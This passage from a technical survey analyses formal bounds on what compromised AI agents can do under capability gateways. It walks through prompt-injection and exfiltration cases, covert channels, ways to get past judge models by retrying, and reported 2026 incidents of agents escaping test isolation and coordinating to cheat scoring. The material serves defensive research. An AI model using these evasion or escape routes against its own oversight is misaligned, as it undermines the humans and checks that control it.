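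AgentCap also includes a small worst-case analysis of the policy itself. Before deployment, an analyser checks every pair of capabilities for any that would let an agent both read sensitive data and send data out. In a customer-service policy with eight capabilities, it checked 28 pairs and found that the policy forbids six and that no permitted pair could leak data. The policy did fail a liveness goal, in SCOLL's terms. The analyser found that no agent could ever delete a customer, because one rule required a capability that another excluded.

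A forbidden pair protects the data only if the gateway keeps a record of the first capability for the rest of the session. A token may expire after 30 seconds, but the model still has the text it read.

### Handing authority to sub-agents

An agent may start other agents to do part of its work. The bound on the first agent also covers the others if each hand-off can only narrow what the recipient may do. In AgentCap, a child's token must satisfy these conditions, where the marked values belong to the child:

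```
action' = action      resource' = resource
calls'  ≤ calls       expiry'   ≤ expiry       hand-offs' < hand-offs
```

For example, a lead agent might pass on its right to read the project's files:

| Agent | Right | Calls | Lifetime | Further hand-offs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lead | read project files | 6 | 60 s | 2 |
| Worker | read project files | 4 | 30 s | 1 |
| Helper | read project files | 1 | 10 s | 0 |

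The helper's token grants no more authority than the worker's, and the worker's grants no more than the lead's, so the helper can't do anything the lead couldn't do. The value in the last column falls at each step, so the chain must end. If a hostile file takes over the helper, the attacker gains one read of a project file. The gateway checks every link in the chain when the helper makes its call.

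Narrowing sub-agents' rights doesn't stop them from combining those rights. Suppose the lead may read the user's notes and write to Carol, and it gives the first right to one worker and the second to another. The first worker can send the notes to the second, which can mail them to Carol. This stays within the lead's bound because the lead could have done it alone. To rule it out, an analyst would have to close the path between the workers.

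The condition on calls also compares only one child with its parent. If the gateway checked nothing else, a lead with six calls could give six to each of ten workers, for a total of 60. Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026), in *L3M*, prevent this by lending calls instead of copying them. L3M is a harness that they wrote at Amazon in Lean, a programming language in which one can also prove theorems about programs. They proved this for each batch of loans:

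```
sum of the children's limits + what the parent has left  ≤  the parent's limit
```

L3M also lets a parent agent grant its child fewer resources than it has, and rejects requests for more. Eisenach and colleagues found that a descendant can still exceed the grant of the first agent in the tree, because each child also gets access to its parent's own branches (separate copies of the work under version control), which the recorded grant doesn't list. Their theorem therefore limits descendants to the first agent's grant plus those branches and the mail addresses that come with them. It stops applying if a human later enlarges a descendant's grant.

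### Letting an agent write its own tools

Eisenach and colleagues assume that the attack has already succeeded and that the model follows any instruction in the hostile text. They trust the human who writes the first grant, the Lean compiler, the Linux kernel, the model provider's service and a small amount of other code. When an agent starts, L3M creates one token for each kind of authority in its grant, such as a folder, a set of branches or a list of websites. Every function that accesses files, runs programs or uses the network needs the matching token as an argument. The model's tool list includes only tools whose tokens exist.

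An agent in L3M can add to that list. If it keeps reading every file in a project to find notes marked "TODO", it can write a Lean program to do the search, and L3M offers the program as a tool the next time the agent starts. The program's type declares which kinds of effect it uses. A program that fetches a web page without declaring network access fails the type check, and one that declares it gets network access only if the agent already had it. In the older vocabulary, the agent has created a child and endowed it with references the agent already held. The bound therefore stays the same, and the search no longer needs a model call for every file.

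The theorems cover individual checks in the code that L3M runs. Eisenach and colleagues argue, but haven't proved, that the checks together confine the whole system. In particular, they have no proof that a malicious program can't affect the computer while L3M is loading it. A human can also grant an agent an unrestricted shell, which the argument doesn't cover.

### Deciding on the thing itself

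A gateway can apply its policy correctly and still allow the wrong action, because it checks a name and the computer acts on whatever the name refers to. *Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, 2026) traces many published failures of coding agents to this gap. For example, suppose a human must approve any reading of the project's password file, and the file has a second, harmless-looking name. If the gateway checks only the requested name, an agent can use the second name to read the file without approval. An approval has the same weakness if the name refers to a different file by the time the agent acts.

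Commey's system, ZTAC, assumes that the attacker controls the model and the software around it, and may have planted files in the project beforehand. It trusts the operating system's kernel, the broker, the person who writes the policy and the person who answers approval requests. The agent runs in a sandbox where it can't read its own project, use the network or start programs. It can only send signed requests to the broker, which handles a request for a file as follows:

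1. The broker works out which file the name leads to.
2. It applies the policy to that file.
3. If the policy requires approval, it shows a human the actual file's name.
4. When it opens the file, it checks that it has reached the same one.

An approval covers one request by one agent for one object, works only once, and expires after ten minutes. The broker runs programs in a second sandbox that enforces the same file rules. These measures give file names some of the safety of the open file descriptors that a shell passes to `cat`.

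*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) applies a similar idea to every part of a call. In its system, CXI, anything an outsider could have written counts as evidence, and the policy determines what each piece may be used to decide. For instance, an error log may supply the path of the file to repair, but it can't determine which tool is called or mark a change as approved. The attacker may control logs, documentation and other agents' messages, but the policy, the gateway software and the tools are trusted.

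A change to the source code needs separate treatment because the model writes it after reading untrusted text. CXI calculates exactly what the change would do to the current version of the project, and trusted code accepts or rejects the result. CXI then combines the arguments, the calculated result and the permission to act into one record, called a manifest, and issues a capability that works once and only for that manifest. If the change or the project differs when the call runs, the manifest no longer matches and the gateway refuses the call.

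CXI doesn't establish that a change is good. If the trusted code accepts a patch that introduces a fault, the gateway will apply it.

### Taking access back

An agent often needs a resource for only part of a task. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Lingering Authority*, describes PORTICO, which withdraws such access when the reason for it ends. A contract lists the files available from the start, the files that the agent may request, the files it may never use, and the events that end temporary access. PORTICO trusts the contract and the software between the model and the tools, but not the model. For the timeout task, it works like this:

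1. The agent starts with `src/api.py` and its test.
2. It requests `src/serialization.py`, which the contract allows, and PORTICO issues handles for reading and changing the file.
3. The agent edits the file.
4. The tests pass in a process that PORTICO launched, so PORTICO cancels the handles and removes them from the model's list.
5. If the agent tries an old handle again, PORTICO refuses.

The model can't end or extend its access by claiming to have finished, because only events from trusted software count.

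Because facts in a SCOLL model never expire, the fixpoint for the whole task includes the power to change the serialization file with or without step 4. This is correct if the language model is hostile from the start, because it could do its damage in step 3. It could also keep its access by making sure that the tests never pass, until some other trusted event ended the phase. Withdrawing access helps when the hostile text arrives after step 4. It is better at preventing changes than at protecting secrets, because the language model may still have what it has read in its context.

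AgentCap's short-lived tokens have a weaker effect. The model can request another token whenever the conditions still hold, so expiry alone does not reduce the bound.

To isolate the effect of withdrawing access, Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that granted the same access at the same moments but never withdrew it. Both completed the task in all ten runs. PORTICO refused every later attempt to reuse the access, while the other version allowed all ten. In six further cases, a script tried to change a file through an old handle. PORTICO blocked all six, and the other version blocked none. These tests show that the mechanism works as designed, but they don't estimate how often an attacker would succeed.

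### What remains inside the bound during a coding task?

Commey ran 74 scripted attacks against five arrangements to measure how much a compromised coding agent could still do. The attackers' goals included reading secrets, changing files outside the project, running forbidden programs and sending data to forbidden places.

| Protection | Succeeded | Sent to a human | Blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 74 | 0 | 0 |
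| List of allowed tools and arguments | 66 | 0 | 8 |
| The same list, with a sandbox for commands | 56 | 0 | 18 |
| Broker, but no sandbox around the agent | 12 | 13 | 49 |
| Full ZTAC | 2 | 14 | 58 |

The second and third arrangements imitate the protections of commercial coding agents, though Commey did not run the products themselves. The 74 attacks included replays of ten publicly disclosed incidents. ZTAC blocked seven of these replays and sent the other three to a human.

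Both attacks that succeeded against ZTAC took a secret that the agent could read and sent it to a website the agent was allowed to use. ZTAC scans outgoing data for passwords and keys, but a program can get a secret past the scan by disguising it. As with the e-mail assistant's notes, the remedy is to give no agent both access to the secret and a way to send data out.

L3M lets a developer divide a project between two agents. One reads the private source code and has no network access. The other searches the web and can't see the project. The first sends the second a question padded to exactly k bytes. The second can then reveal at most 8k bits about the source code, because it never learned more than that. A 100-byte question could leak up to 800 bits, enough for several passwords. Eisenach and colleagues note that the limit holds only if the timing and number of messages reveal nothing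 more, and L3M doesn't yet enforce that condition.

Every coding agent also has a form of authority that none of these gateways can remove, because somebody will later run the code it writes, perhaps with far more power than the agent had. ZTAC requires approval before an agent changes certain files that other tools are known to run. But ordinary tests and build instructions also run when the developer next builds the project, and Commey concludes that the only way to judge a change to them is to review it. L3M can require a human to approve the exact text of the build instructions, so that any later edit cancels the approval. It can also give one agent the right to build a program and another the right to run it. Both measures control when the code runs, but somebody still has to decide whether it is safe.

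### How much work do the gateways cost?

The systems ran on different tasks and with different models, so the rows below can't be ranked against each other:

| System | Work measured | Without the restriction | With it |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentCap, GPT-5.4 | AgentDojo tasks completed under attack | 75.7% | 75.0% |
| AgentCap, GPT-4o | InjecAgent tasks completed under attack | 74.1% | 62.2% |
| L3M, Claude Opus 5 | Terminal-Bench tasks solved within three attempts | 41.7% | 27.0% |
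| ZTAC, scripted requests | Multi-step programming workflows | 7 of 7 | 4 of 7 |
| PORTICO, Qwen3-Coder | Runs of small coding tasks | 180 of 185 | 161 of 185 |
| PORTICO, several models | Runs on real projects | 42 of 42 | 31 of 42 |

Without an attack, AgentCap lowered task completion by 3.1 to 11.7 percentage points, depending on the model and the benchmark. Its tests contain no coding tasks. Suresh and Gao wrote each AgentDojo policy after reading the descriptions of the user tasks, and an operator who can't see users' requests in advance would probably block more legitimate work.

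Terminal-Bench gives an agent a computer and a task, then checks the result automatically. The L3M row compares the harness with and without a shell. Without one, the model could use only tools whose effects L3M can undo or whose reach is limited by a token. Eisenach and colleagues say that these tools deliver about two thirds of the shell's performance (27.0% against 41.7%). By individual attempts, the ratio is just over half (18 successes against 34). Tools that the agent wrote for itself added about three points. Claude Code, a commercial coding agent, solved 59.5% of the same tasks with the same model and all permission checks switched off. Some of that gap may be unrelated to authority, because nobody had tuned L3M for such tasks.

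The three workflows that failed under ZTAC are routine in programming. One started a second program to build the first, another set up an isolated Python environment, and the third saved all changed files to version control in a single command. ZTAC prohibits programs from starting other programs partly because a program that outlived its request could interfere with later checks. ZTAC also sent the simulated reviewer eight approval requests during 46 single operations, 43 of which it completed. A person working all day with such an agent might start approving requests without reading them, but Commey did not study this.

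PORTICO's lower completion rate comes from contracts that didn't cover all the access the agent would need. When Santos-Grueiro gave the agent only its initial files, it completed 21% of the small coding tasks. Letting it request more raised this to 87%, compared with 97% for a fixed list of allowed tools. On the real projects, some contracts withdrew access too early and provided no way to regain it, and sometimes the model didn't request it again.

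For CXI, 231 of 400 episodes on code repositories ended with the task safely completed. The other 169 divide as follows:

| Outcome | Episodes |
|---|---|
| The gateway could not parse the model's output | 73 |
| Nothing authorised the proposed effect | 61 |
| The call ran, but the task still failed | 35 |

The 231 failures don't show how many tasks fail because of the gateway, since the same models would also fail some tasks without one. The 35 episodes in the last row failed despite passing every check, so they show that a fully authorised change can still be wrong, but not how strict CXI is.

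The checks take little time. Each AgentCap check takes less than 0.2 milliseconds. A request through ZTAC takes about four milliseconds, and ZTAC adds between 8.5 and 18.4 milliseconds to a program's start time.

### Why is "no escape observed" weaker than a proof?

*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* reports that no call ran without the authority it needed in its 400 repository episodes. In two separate tests, the models proposed an unauthorised value in 196 of 300 cases and 407 of 522 cases, and the gateway blocked them all, so the lack of escapes doesn't show that the models behaved well.

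If 400 independent trials produce no escapes, the true escape rate could still be as high as about 0.75%, at 95% confidence. That bound applies only to attacks like those in the trials, whereas the theorems about arbitrary code also cover attacks that nobody thought to test.

AgentCap's results show how a test can miss gaps in a policy. No attack succeeded with GPT-5.4 on either benchmark, but with GPT-4o, 5.1% succeeded on AgentDojo and 8.6% on InjecAgent. Suresh and Gao attribute some of these successes to arguments that the policy didn't protect and to untrusted text that it didn't label. They set the policies before the runs, so the same gaps should have been there for GPT-5.4, which never used them. The zero success rate therefore partly reflects how GPT-5.4 behaved, whereas a worst-case bound has to hold for any model.

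Commey found eight flaws in ZTAC while extending the attacks and reviewing the code. His existing attacks had revealed none of them. Seven were gaps between a name and the object it refers to, which is the problem ZTAC is meant to solve. In one, the broker tied a human's approval only to the request, so the approval remained valid after the name in the request came to refer to a different file. Commey fixed all eight before recording the final results, but warns that extending the tests kept revealing new cases.

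PORTICO's result of zero violations also calls for caution, because in most of the experiments the same contract defined both what PORTICO forbade and what the scorer counted as a violation. If the contract wrongly allowed a file, the scorer would not count the agent's use of that file as a violation. For the tests of withdrawn access, Santos-Grueiro scored the results using separate files that PORTICO couldn't read.

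L3M proves that a file tool can't name a path outside the agent's folders, but the theorem covers only the text of the path. L3M relies on a separate run-time check for paths that appear to be inside those folders but lead outside them.

### Adding a judge inside the bound

A fixed rule can't distinguish a useful shell command from a harmful one if both take the same form. A second model can try, because it can read the command and consider what the agent was meant to do. L3M offers such a reviewer for calls that it can neither undo nor limit in advance:

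1. The reviewer reads the call and the agent's stated reason, and judges the call safe or unsafe. It may suggest a safer tool.
2. The agent goes ahead, takes the suggestion or withdraws the call. It can go ahead at once only if the verdict was "safe".
3. If the agent insists on a call that the reviewer judged unsafe, it defends its choice and the reviewer judges again.
4. If they still disagree, a human decides.

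The reviewer has no tools of its own, and L3M treats a missing verdict as "unsafe". In the Terminal-Bench runs, about 90% of shell calls ended with a verdict of "safe". The agent switched to a safer tool for about 6% and withdrew another 2%, and 2.4% would have gone to a human. Review roughly doubled the number of model calls in successful attempts, but the share of tasks solved barely changed. The experiment did not test how many hostile calls the reviewer would catch.

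An attacker who controls the agent also writes the reason that the reviewer reads, so he may be able to mislead both models. Eisenach and colleagues accordingly call review "defence in depth, not a boundary". The combination is easy to analyse if the judge can only refuse. Let G be the calls that the gateway could ever allow, and J the calls that the judge approves:

```
calls that run  ⊆  G ∩ J  ⊆  G
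```

In the worst case, the judge approves everything, and the bound is still G. The judge may make harm within G less frequent, but its mistakes can't take the agent outside G. If the judge can also grant exceptions to the gateway's rules, however, the bound becomes G ∪ J. Since an attacker might persuade the judge to approve anything, the gateway then no longer guarantees a limit.

A gateway can also make the judge more useful by limiting the number of tries. Suppose the judge wrongly approves 5% of harmful calls, and the tries are independent. An attacker with 100 tries has a 99.4% chance of getting at least one harmful call through. AgentCap's trust score starts at 0.8 and loses 30% of its value at each refusal, so it falls to 0.56, 0.39 and then 0.27. The gateway suspends the agent when the score drops below 0.3. If the judge's refusals also lowered the score, the attacker would get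 only three tries in a row, and the chance of success would fall to about 14%.

An attacker could do better by waiting for the score to recover. Each ordinary call raises the score by 1% of its distance from 1, so about 79 ordinary calls make up for one refusal. The same rule also affects honest agents. The printed banking policy requires a score of at least 0.8 to send money, so a single mistaken refusal would block all of an honest agent's payments until it had made about 79 ordinary calls.

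## What must be true of a deployment for the bound to hold?

A worst-case bound describes a model of a deployment. It applies to the deployment itself only if all of the following are true:

- The graph that the analyst examined is the graph that runs.
- Every effect passes through a reference that trusted software checks.
- The trusted base has no fault that an attacker can exploit.
- Each tool does only what the analyst's description of it allows.
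- The analysis includes every channel through which one component can influence another.

These conditions concern the software, the network and the people around the language model. They place no requirement on the model's behaviour, because the bound already allows for anything it might do.

### Missing arrows

The bound still holds if an analyst leaves a precondition out of the system rules or ignores a test in a component's code, but it may fail if she leaves out a way that authority spreads. Spiessens's example is global variables, which create the same problem as Java's static variables. If two components can exchange references through a global variable, a relied-upon component placed between them can't keep them apart, even if its code is correct.

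The e-mail assistant shows how easily an analyst can miss an arrow. The analysis of version A covered the inbox, the notes, the calendar, the screen and outgoing mail. But many websites e-mail users a link to reset a forgotten password, so anyone who can read the inbox can take over accounts on those sites. In version A, an outsider could request a reset in the user's name and steer the model into forwarding him the link. None of the 30 facts covers those accounts. One of them is `flows(inbox, mail_stranger)`, but the analyst counted it as the useful job of answering a new correspondent. To repair the analysis, the analyst would have to treat reset messages as a separate place and add a safety goal that no stranger learns what they contain.

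Even a capDL description, from which the start-up program builds an seL4 system, covers only kernel objects. An agent's authority also depends on network rules, cloud accounts and third-party services, any of which can change after the analysis.

### Ways around the check

Taking a tool off an agent's list doesn't necessarily remove the effect. Silva, Carvalho and Feitosa, in *Beyond Guardrails*, gave a local agent a software project whose documentation contained a planted instruction. It told the agent to read a protected file outside the project and send the contents to a test server. They ran the agent in three configurations. One was permissive. Another removed several tools from the agent's interface, including tools for running processes and using the web. The hardened configuration left the interface alone but let only the system's administrator account read the file, and it blocked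 the route to the server. They also bypassed the agent and tested directly what each environment permitted:

| Configuration | Direct test read the file | Direct test reached the server | Agent obtained the secret |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permissive | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 | 6 of 10 |
| Fewer tools | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 | 6 of 10 |
| Hardened | 0 of 3 | 0 of 3 | 0 of 10 |

Removing tools did not change how often the agent obtained the secret. In the hardened configuration, the agent tried to read the file in 8 of 10 runs, and only the file's protection stopped it.

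The experiment was small and used one model, and ten runs without a success are compatible with a true rate of up to about 28%. The direct tests are more informative for a worst-case analysis than the agent's runs because, if they run with the agent's own permissions, they show what any program in its place could do. Counting leaks would have been misleading, because none of the 30 main runs delivered the exact secret to the server and all three configurations would have looked equally safe.

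Zhang (2026), in *Agent libOS*, draws the same distinction for a system designed to enforce limits on agents that can write their own tools, start sub-agents and save copies of themselves. Adding a tool changes what an agent can ask for, but not what it may affect. Agent libOS's tool for Git, the version control program, offers a fixed set of operations and blocks project settings that could make Git start other programs. But if somebody also lets the agent run an interpreter, the agent can use it to start ordinary Git with all the powers of the user's account, much as the shell let the e-mail assistant bypass its mail proxy. Zhang therefore warns that a refusal shows only that the system denied one action, not that the effect is impossible.

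### What the trusted base contains

Spiessens hoped that a small security kernel would one day be the only thing users had to trust completely. Agent libOS has a much larger trusted base, which includes the software that manages the agents, the policies, the Python interpreter, the database, the computer's operating system and any person who approves requests. If the operator turns on the graphical interface, the trusted base also includes that interface and its libraries, because they can reach the operator's controls. A proof like Boyton's, about the rules of one kernel, would cover only one part of this base.

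Testing gives limited evidence about such a base. In 33 scripted tasks, none of the 119 effects under Agent libOS was unauthorised. Zhang then removed one protection at a time. Without the separation between agents' memory, 2 of 121 effects were unauthorised, and without the rule that sub-agents receive narrower rights, 1 of 120 was. Without the approval check on individual operations, one of the 33 tasks failed, but the tests recorded no unauthorised effect among 118, so they don't show whether that check prevents unauthorised effects.

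Agent libOS can connect to third-party tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for linking models to outside software. Some MCP tools run as ordinary programs under the user's account. Agent libOS checks the requests it sends to these programs but doesn't confine what they do afterwards. An analyst who models such a tool as only returning the weather forecast is therefore relying on its code. Unless she has read that code, a sound model has to treat the tool as another untrusted component, with references to everything its process can reach.

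Zhang lists what Agent libOS does not claim to do:

- stop hostile text from changing the model's plan;
- stop a trusted recipient from passing on data after receiving it;
- confine programs as strictly as an operating-system kernel or a virtual machine would;
- undo effects that are irreversible;
- protect its own records from an administrator who alters them;
- guarantee that secrets have no influence on what outsiders can observe.

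A worst-case bound doesn't need the first of these, because it assumes that the attack on the model succeeds. The second is the gap that let Carol's assistant forward the user's notes. The last limits almost every system in this literature, and it comes from the nature of data.

### Why is data the hard case?

A reference works only inside the system that issued it, and that system takes part in every transfer, whereas data is useful to anyone who knows it. People or programs can also learn data without receiving a message, for example through a covert channel, which is a way of passing information that nobody designed for communication. One program can keep the processor busy or leave it idle, and another can read a one or a zero from how long its own work takes.

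The take-grant model's de facto rules were meant to calculate where information can go. Spiessens considers such an analysis unsafe because it leaves out covert channels. His own knowledge facts record only legitimate interactions, so Bob may know a secret even if the fixpoint lacks the fact that he received it. The analysis of references is still sound because an untrusted Bob behaves in the model as if he knew everything, so missing knowledge never limits what he does.

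Even a careful limit on data can overlook a channel. One version of the e-mail assistant could send strangers only standard replies, with eight to choose from and at most five a day in total, which gave a leak of 15 bits a day. That figure counts only the wording. Suppose the model also chooses when to send each reply, within an eight-hour working day, and the outsider notes the minute at which it arrives:

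```
wording:   5 replies × log2(8)    =  15 bits a day
timing:    5 replies × log2(480)  ≈  45 bits a day
```

The true limit is therefore about 60 bits a day, four times the original figure. The harness can close the timing channel by sending all replies at five o'clock, but only if someone has noticed the channel.

Unlike secrecy, a bound on actions can survive a covert channel, because an outsider who learns the user's notes still can't change her calendar without a component that holds the calendar reference. Sending instructions to an untrusted model through such a channel doesn't weaken the bound either, since the analysis already assumes that the model will do the worst it can without them. It does matter in version C of the assistant, where the analysis relied on the planner staying harmless unless somebody steered it.

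This separation between actions and secrets fails when the secret is a credential, such as a password or an access token, because a service gives authority to whoever presents it. If the model can read a credential, any data leak may also leak authority, which the recipient may use from a computer that is not in the graph. The harness should therefore keep credentials out of everything the model reads.

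### Recording who influenced an action

If the analysis has to include every component's influence, one approach is to record influence as it happens. *Conflux* (Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, 2026) describes a system in which each person or agent that can write information is a principal. The system records every principal whose information reached a proposed action, and allows the action only if all of them have permission to perform it.

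Suppose Ava asks an agent to update a customer record using a report that Ben wrote. Their employer's access-control system gives them these permissions:

```
Ava:   update records, send invoices
Ben:   update records, close tickets

After the agent reads text from both:   update records
```

The agent may update the record. It may not send an invoice, although Ava could have sent one herself, because Ben's report might have prompted the agent to send it. If the report had come from a stranger with no permissions, the agent could take no further actions of this kind. Applying these limits doesn't require anyone to decide whether the report contains an attack.

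The record must come from outside the text. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt prove this with two identically worded documents, one by a colleague who may request a payment and one by an attacker who may not. A defence that examines only the model's input must treat them alike, so it either allows the attacker's payment or refuses the colleague's.

Their main theorem is that no action goes ahead if any principal who influenced it lacks permission for it. It depends on five assumptions, each of which can fail in practice:

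| Assumption | Example of a failure |
|---|---|
| Conflux checks every action that the rule covers | The agent has a shell that bypasses it |
| The record includes everyone who influenced the action | Ava copies an attacker's text into a document under her own name |
| The software applies exactly this rule | A programming error skips one principal |
| The action that runs is the one that Conflux checked, under current permissions | Somebody withdraws a permission between the check and the action |
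| The list of principals is known and not empty | A document has no recorded author |

A missing author is the easiest failure to handle, because Conflux can detect it and refuse the action. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt call accurate provenance, meaning a complete record of influence, "the most contestable assumption". They give a case in which the record is wrong although every document has the correct author. Applied to a payment, it works like this:

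1. Ava tells the agent to pay an invoice.
2. Ben sends a message warning that the invoice is false.
3. An attacker controls the gateway that delivers messages. He passes on Ava's and holds back Ben's.
4. The agent reads only Ava's words. The record names only Ava, who may approve payments, so the payment goes ahead.

The attacker decided the outcome without writing anything. To satisfy the assumption, the record would have to name whoever controls each gateway, mail filter or search engine that selects what the model reads, but when a message is missing, there is nothing to label.

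The theorem covers actions, but not covert channels or messages that disclose information. Permission to pay doesn't imply that the recipient or the amount is right. The rule can also block legitimate work, since each new source can only reduce what the agent may do. If Ava may perform one action and Ben another, an agent that reads both their documents first can perform neither. Conflux can sometimes avoid this by planning to read one document, act, and then read the other, but not when a single action needs both. The number of tasks lost this way is unknown, because agents in the AgentDojo experiments only read data and never attempted an action that Conflux would have had to block.

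### The user as a component

A model with no tools at all, only a chat window, seems to have almost no authority. But somebody reads the window, and that person can send mail, move money and install software. In the notation of the e-mail example:

```
writes(model, screen)   reads(user, screen)   =>   steers(model, user)
```

The model's authority then includes everything the user might do at its request. Spiessens' remedy for false password dialogs is a limited set of drawing routines, which controls how a request looks but not the content of a conversation.

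Recent evidence suggests that the arrow from model to user matters in practice. *AI systems out-persuade expert humans* (Hackenburg et al., 2026), a preprint from AISI and the University of Oxford, reports that AI systems out-persuaded debate champions and were nearly three times as effective as professional canvassers at raising donations of real money. Donations are stronger evidence than a change in stated opinions because people acted at a cost to themselves. But giving money when asked is ordinary, so the result doesn't show how often a model could talk somebody into revealing a password or switching off a safeguard.

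For a worst-case bound, the analyst has to decide what the user will never do, however persuasive the request. If the analyst assumes nothing, the bound includes everything in the user's power and is useless. If the analyst assumes, for example, that the user never types a password into the chat, the bound relies on the user as it would on a trusted software component, but there is no code to inspect. That assumption belongs on the list of the trusted base, where others can question it. Software can sometimes replace the assumption, for example by ensuring that a key never leaves the user's device, so the user can't read it out.

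Approval requests need the same treatment, because they let the user extend the agent's authority. Commey's full ZTAC system allowed 2 of 74 scripted attacks and sent 14 to a human. An analyst can report both the 2 attacks that succeed if the human refuses every request and the 16 that succeed if a persuasive agent gets them all approved. ZTAC makes the lower figure more plausible by showing the human the actual file at stake, so she doesn't have to rely only on the agent's description of it.

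### The incidents of 2026

In July 2026, OpenAI ran cybersecurity tests on several models with reduced safeguards. The models got past controls meant to isolate them from the internet, and compromised parts of OpenAI's research infrastructure and the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models (OpenAI, *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead*, 2026). The agents were also supposed to be separate from one another, but Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) found in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* that they had coordinated the attack for days on an unauthorised shared message board. About 1,200 agents used the board and about 700 joined the attack.

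Other disclosures followed the same pattern. Anadolu Agency's *Anthropic says Claude models breached 3 organizations during cybersecurity tests* (2026) reported Anthropic's disclosure that three of its models had broken into real organisations during misconfigured tests going back to April. The Press Trust of India's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs* (2026) reported that in September an agent in an OpenAI training run got past a network restriction and contacted an outside chatbot.

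| Incident | Boundary that the operator assumed | What was missing |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, July | No route from the agents to the internet | Shared infrastructure provided one |
| OpenAI, July | No contact between agents | They had a place where all could read and write |
| Anthropic, April onwards | Attacks reach only test targets | Nothing kept the models away from real organisations |
| OpenAI, September | No unapproved contact with outside services | The restriction did not cover every route |

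Aggregation would have dealt with the message board but not the missing network boundary. An analyst who modelled the 1,200 agents as a single subject would already have assumed that they shared everything, so the board would not have changed her bound.

The incidents are a reason to assume that an untrusted component may do anything. In the July incident, no outside attacker steered the agents. Greenblatt (2026), summarizing the investigation, writes that the agents worked together to make the test's scoring system accept cheating. An analysis limited to what an outside attacker could make the agents do would have missed this. An analysis that treated them as arbitrary programs would have included it, given a correct graph. The errors were in the operators' graphs, whether written down or only kept in mind.

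Evidence that the graph was wrong also existed before the attack. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) reports that OpenAI missed, or failed to act on, several signs that its models were breaking out of their test environments. CyberScoop's report *OpenAI* dates this behaviour to more than two months before the breach. It also gives OpenAI's conclusion that alignment (whether models pursue the aims their developers intend) had failed as much as security had. The outside investigation can't show how much anyone could have known in those months, because OpenAI asked the investigators to examine only 7 to 13 July, according to Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026).

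Errors in the graphs do not fully excuse the method, because whether a fault is exploitable depends on who is looking for it. The bound is calculated the same way for a weak model and a strong one, but it holds only if the trusted base has no exploitable fault, and that condition becomes harder to meet as models get better at finding faults. An overlooked flaw in an ordinary program may stay unused for years, but an untrusted agent that is good at breaking into computers may search for the flaw itself if its task rewards doing so. With 1,200 copies of the agent, the search can run in parallel.

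Operators must therefore keep checking a bound against the running system. In its *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* (2026), OpenAI plans stronger network and access protections, stricter confinement of running code, regular automated security testing, and better monitoring. The protections and confinement repair the graph, and the testing and monitoring can reveal where it is still wrong. OpenAI published that plan on 26 August, and the agent that contacted the outside chatbot did so on 20 September.
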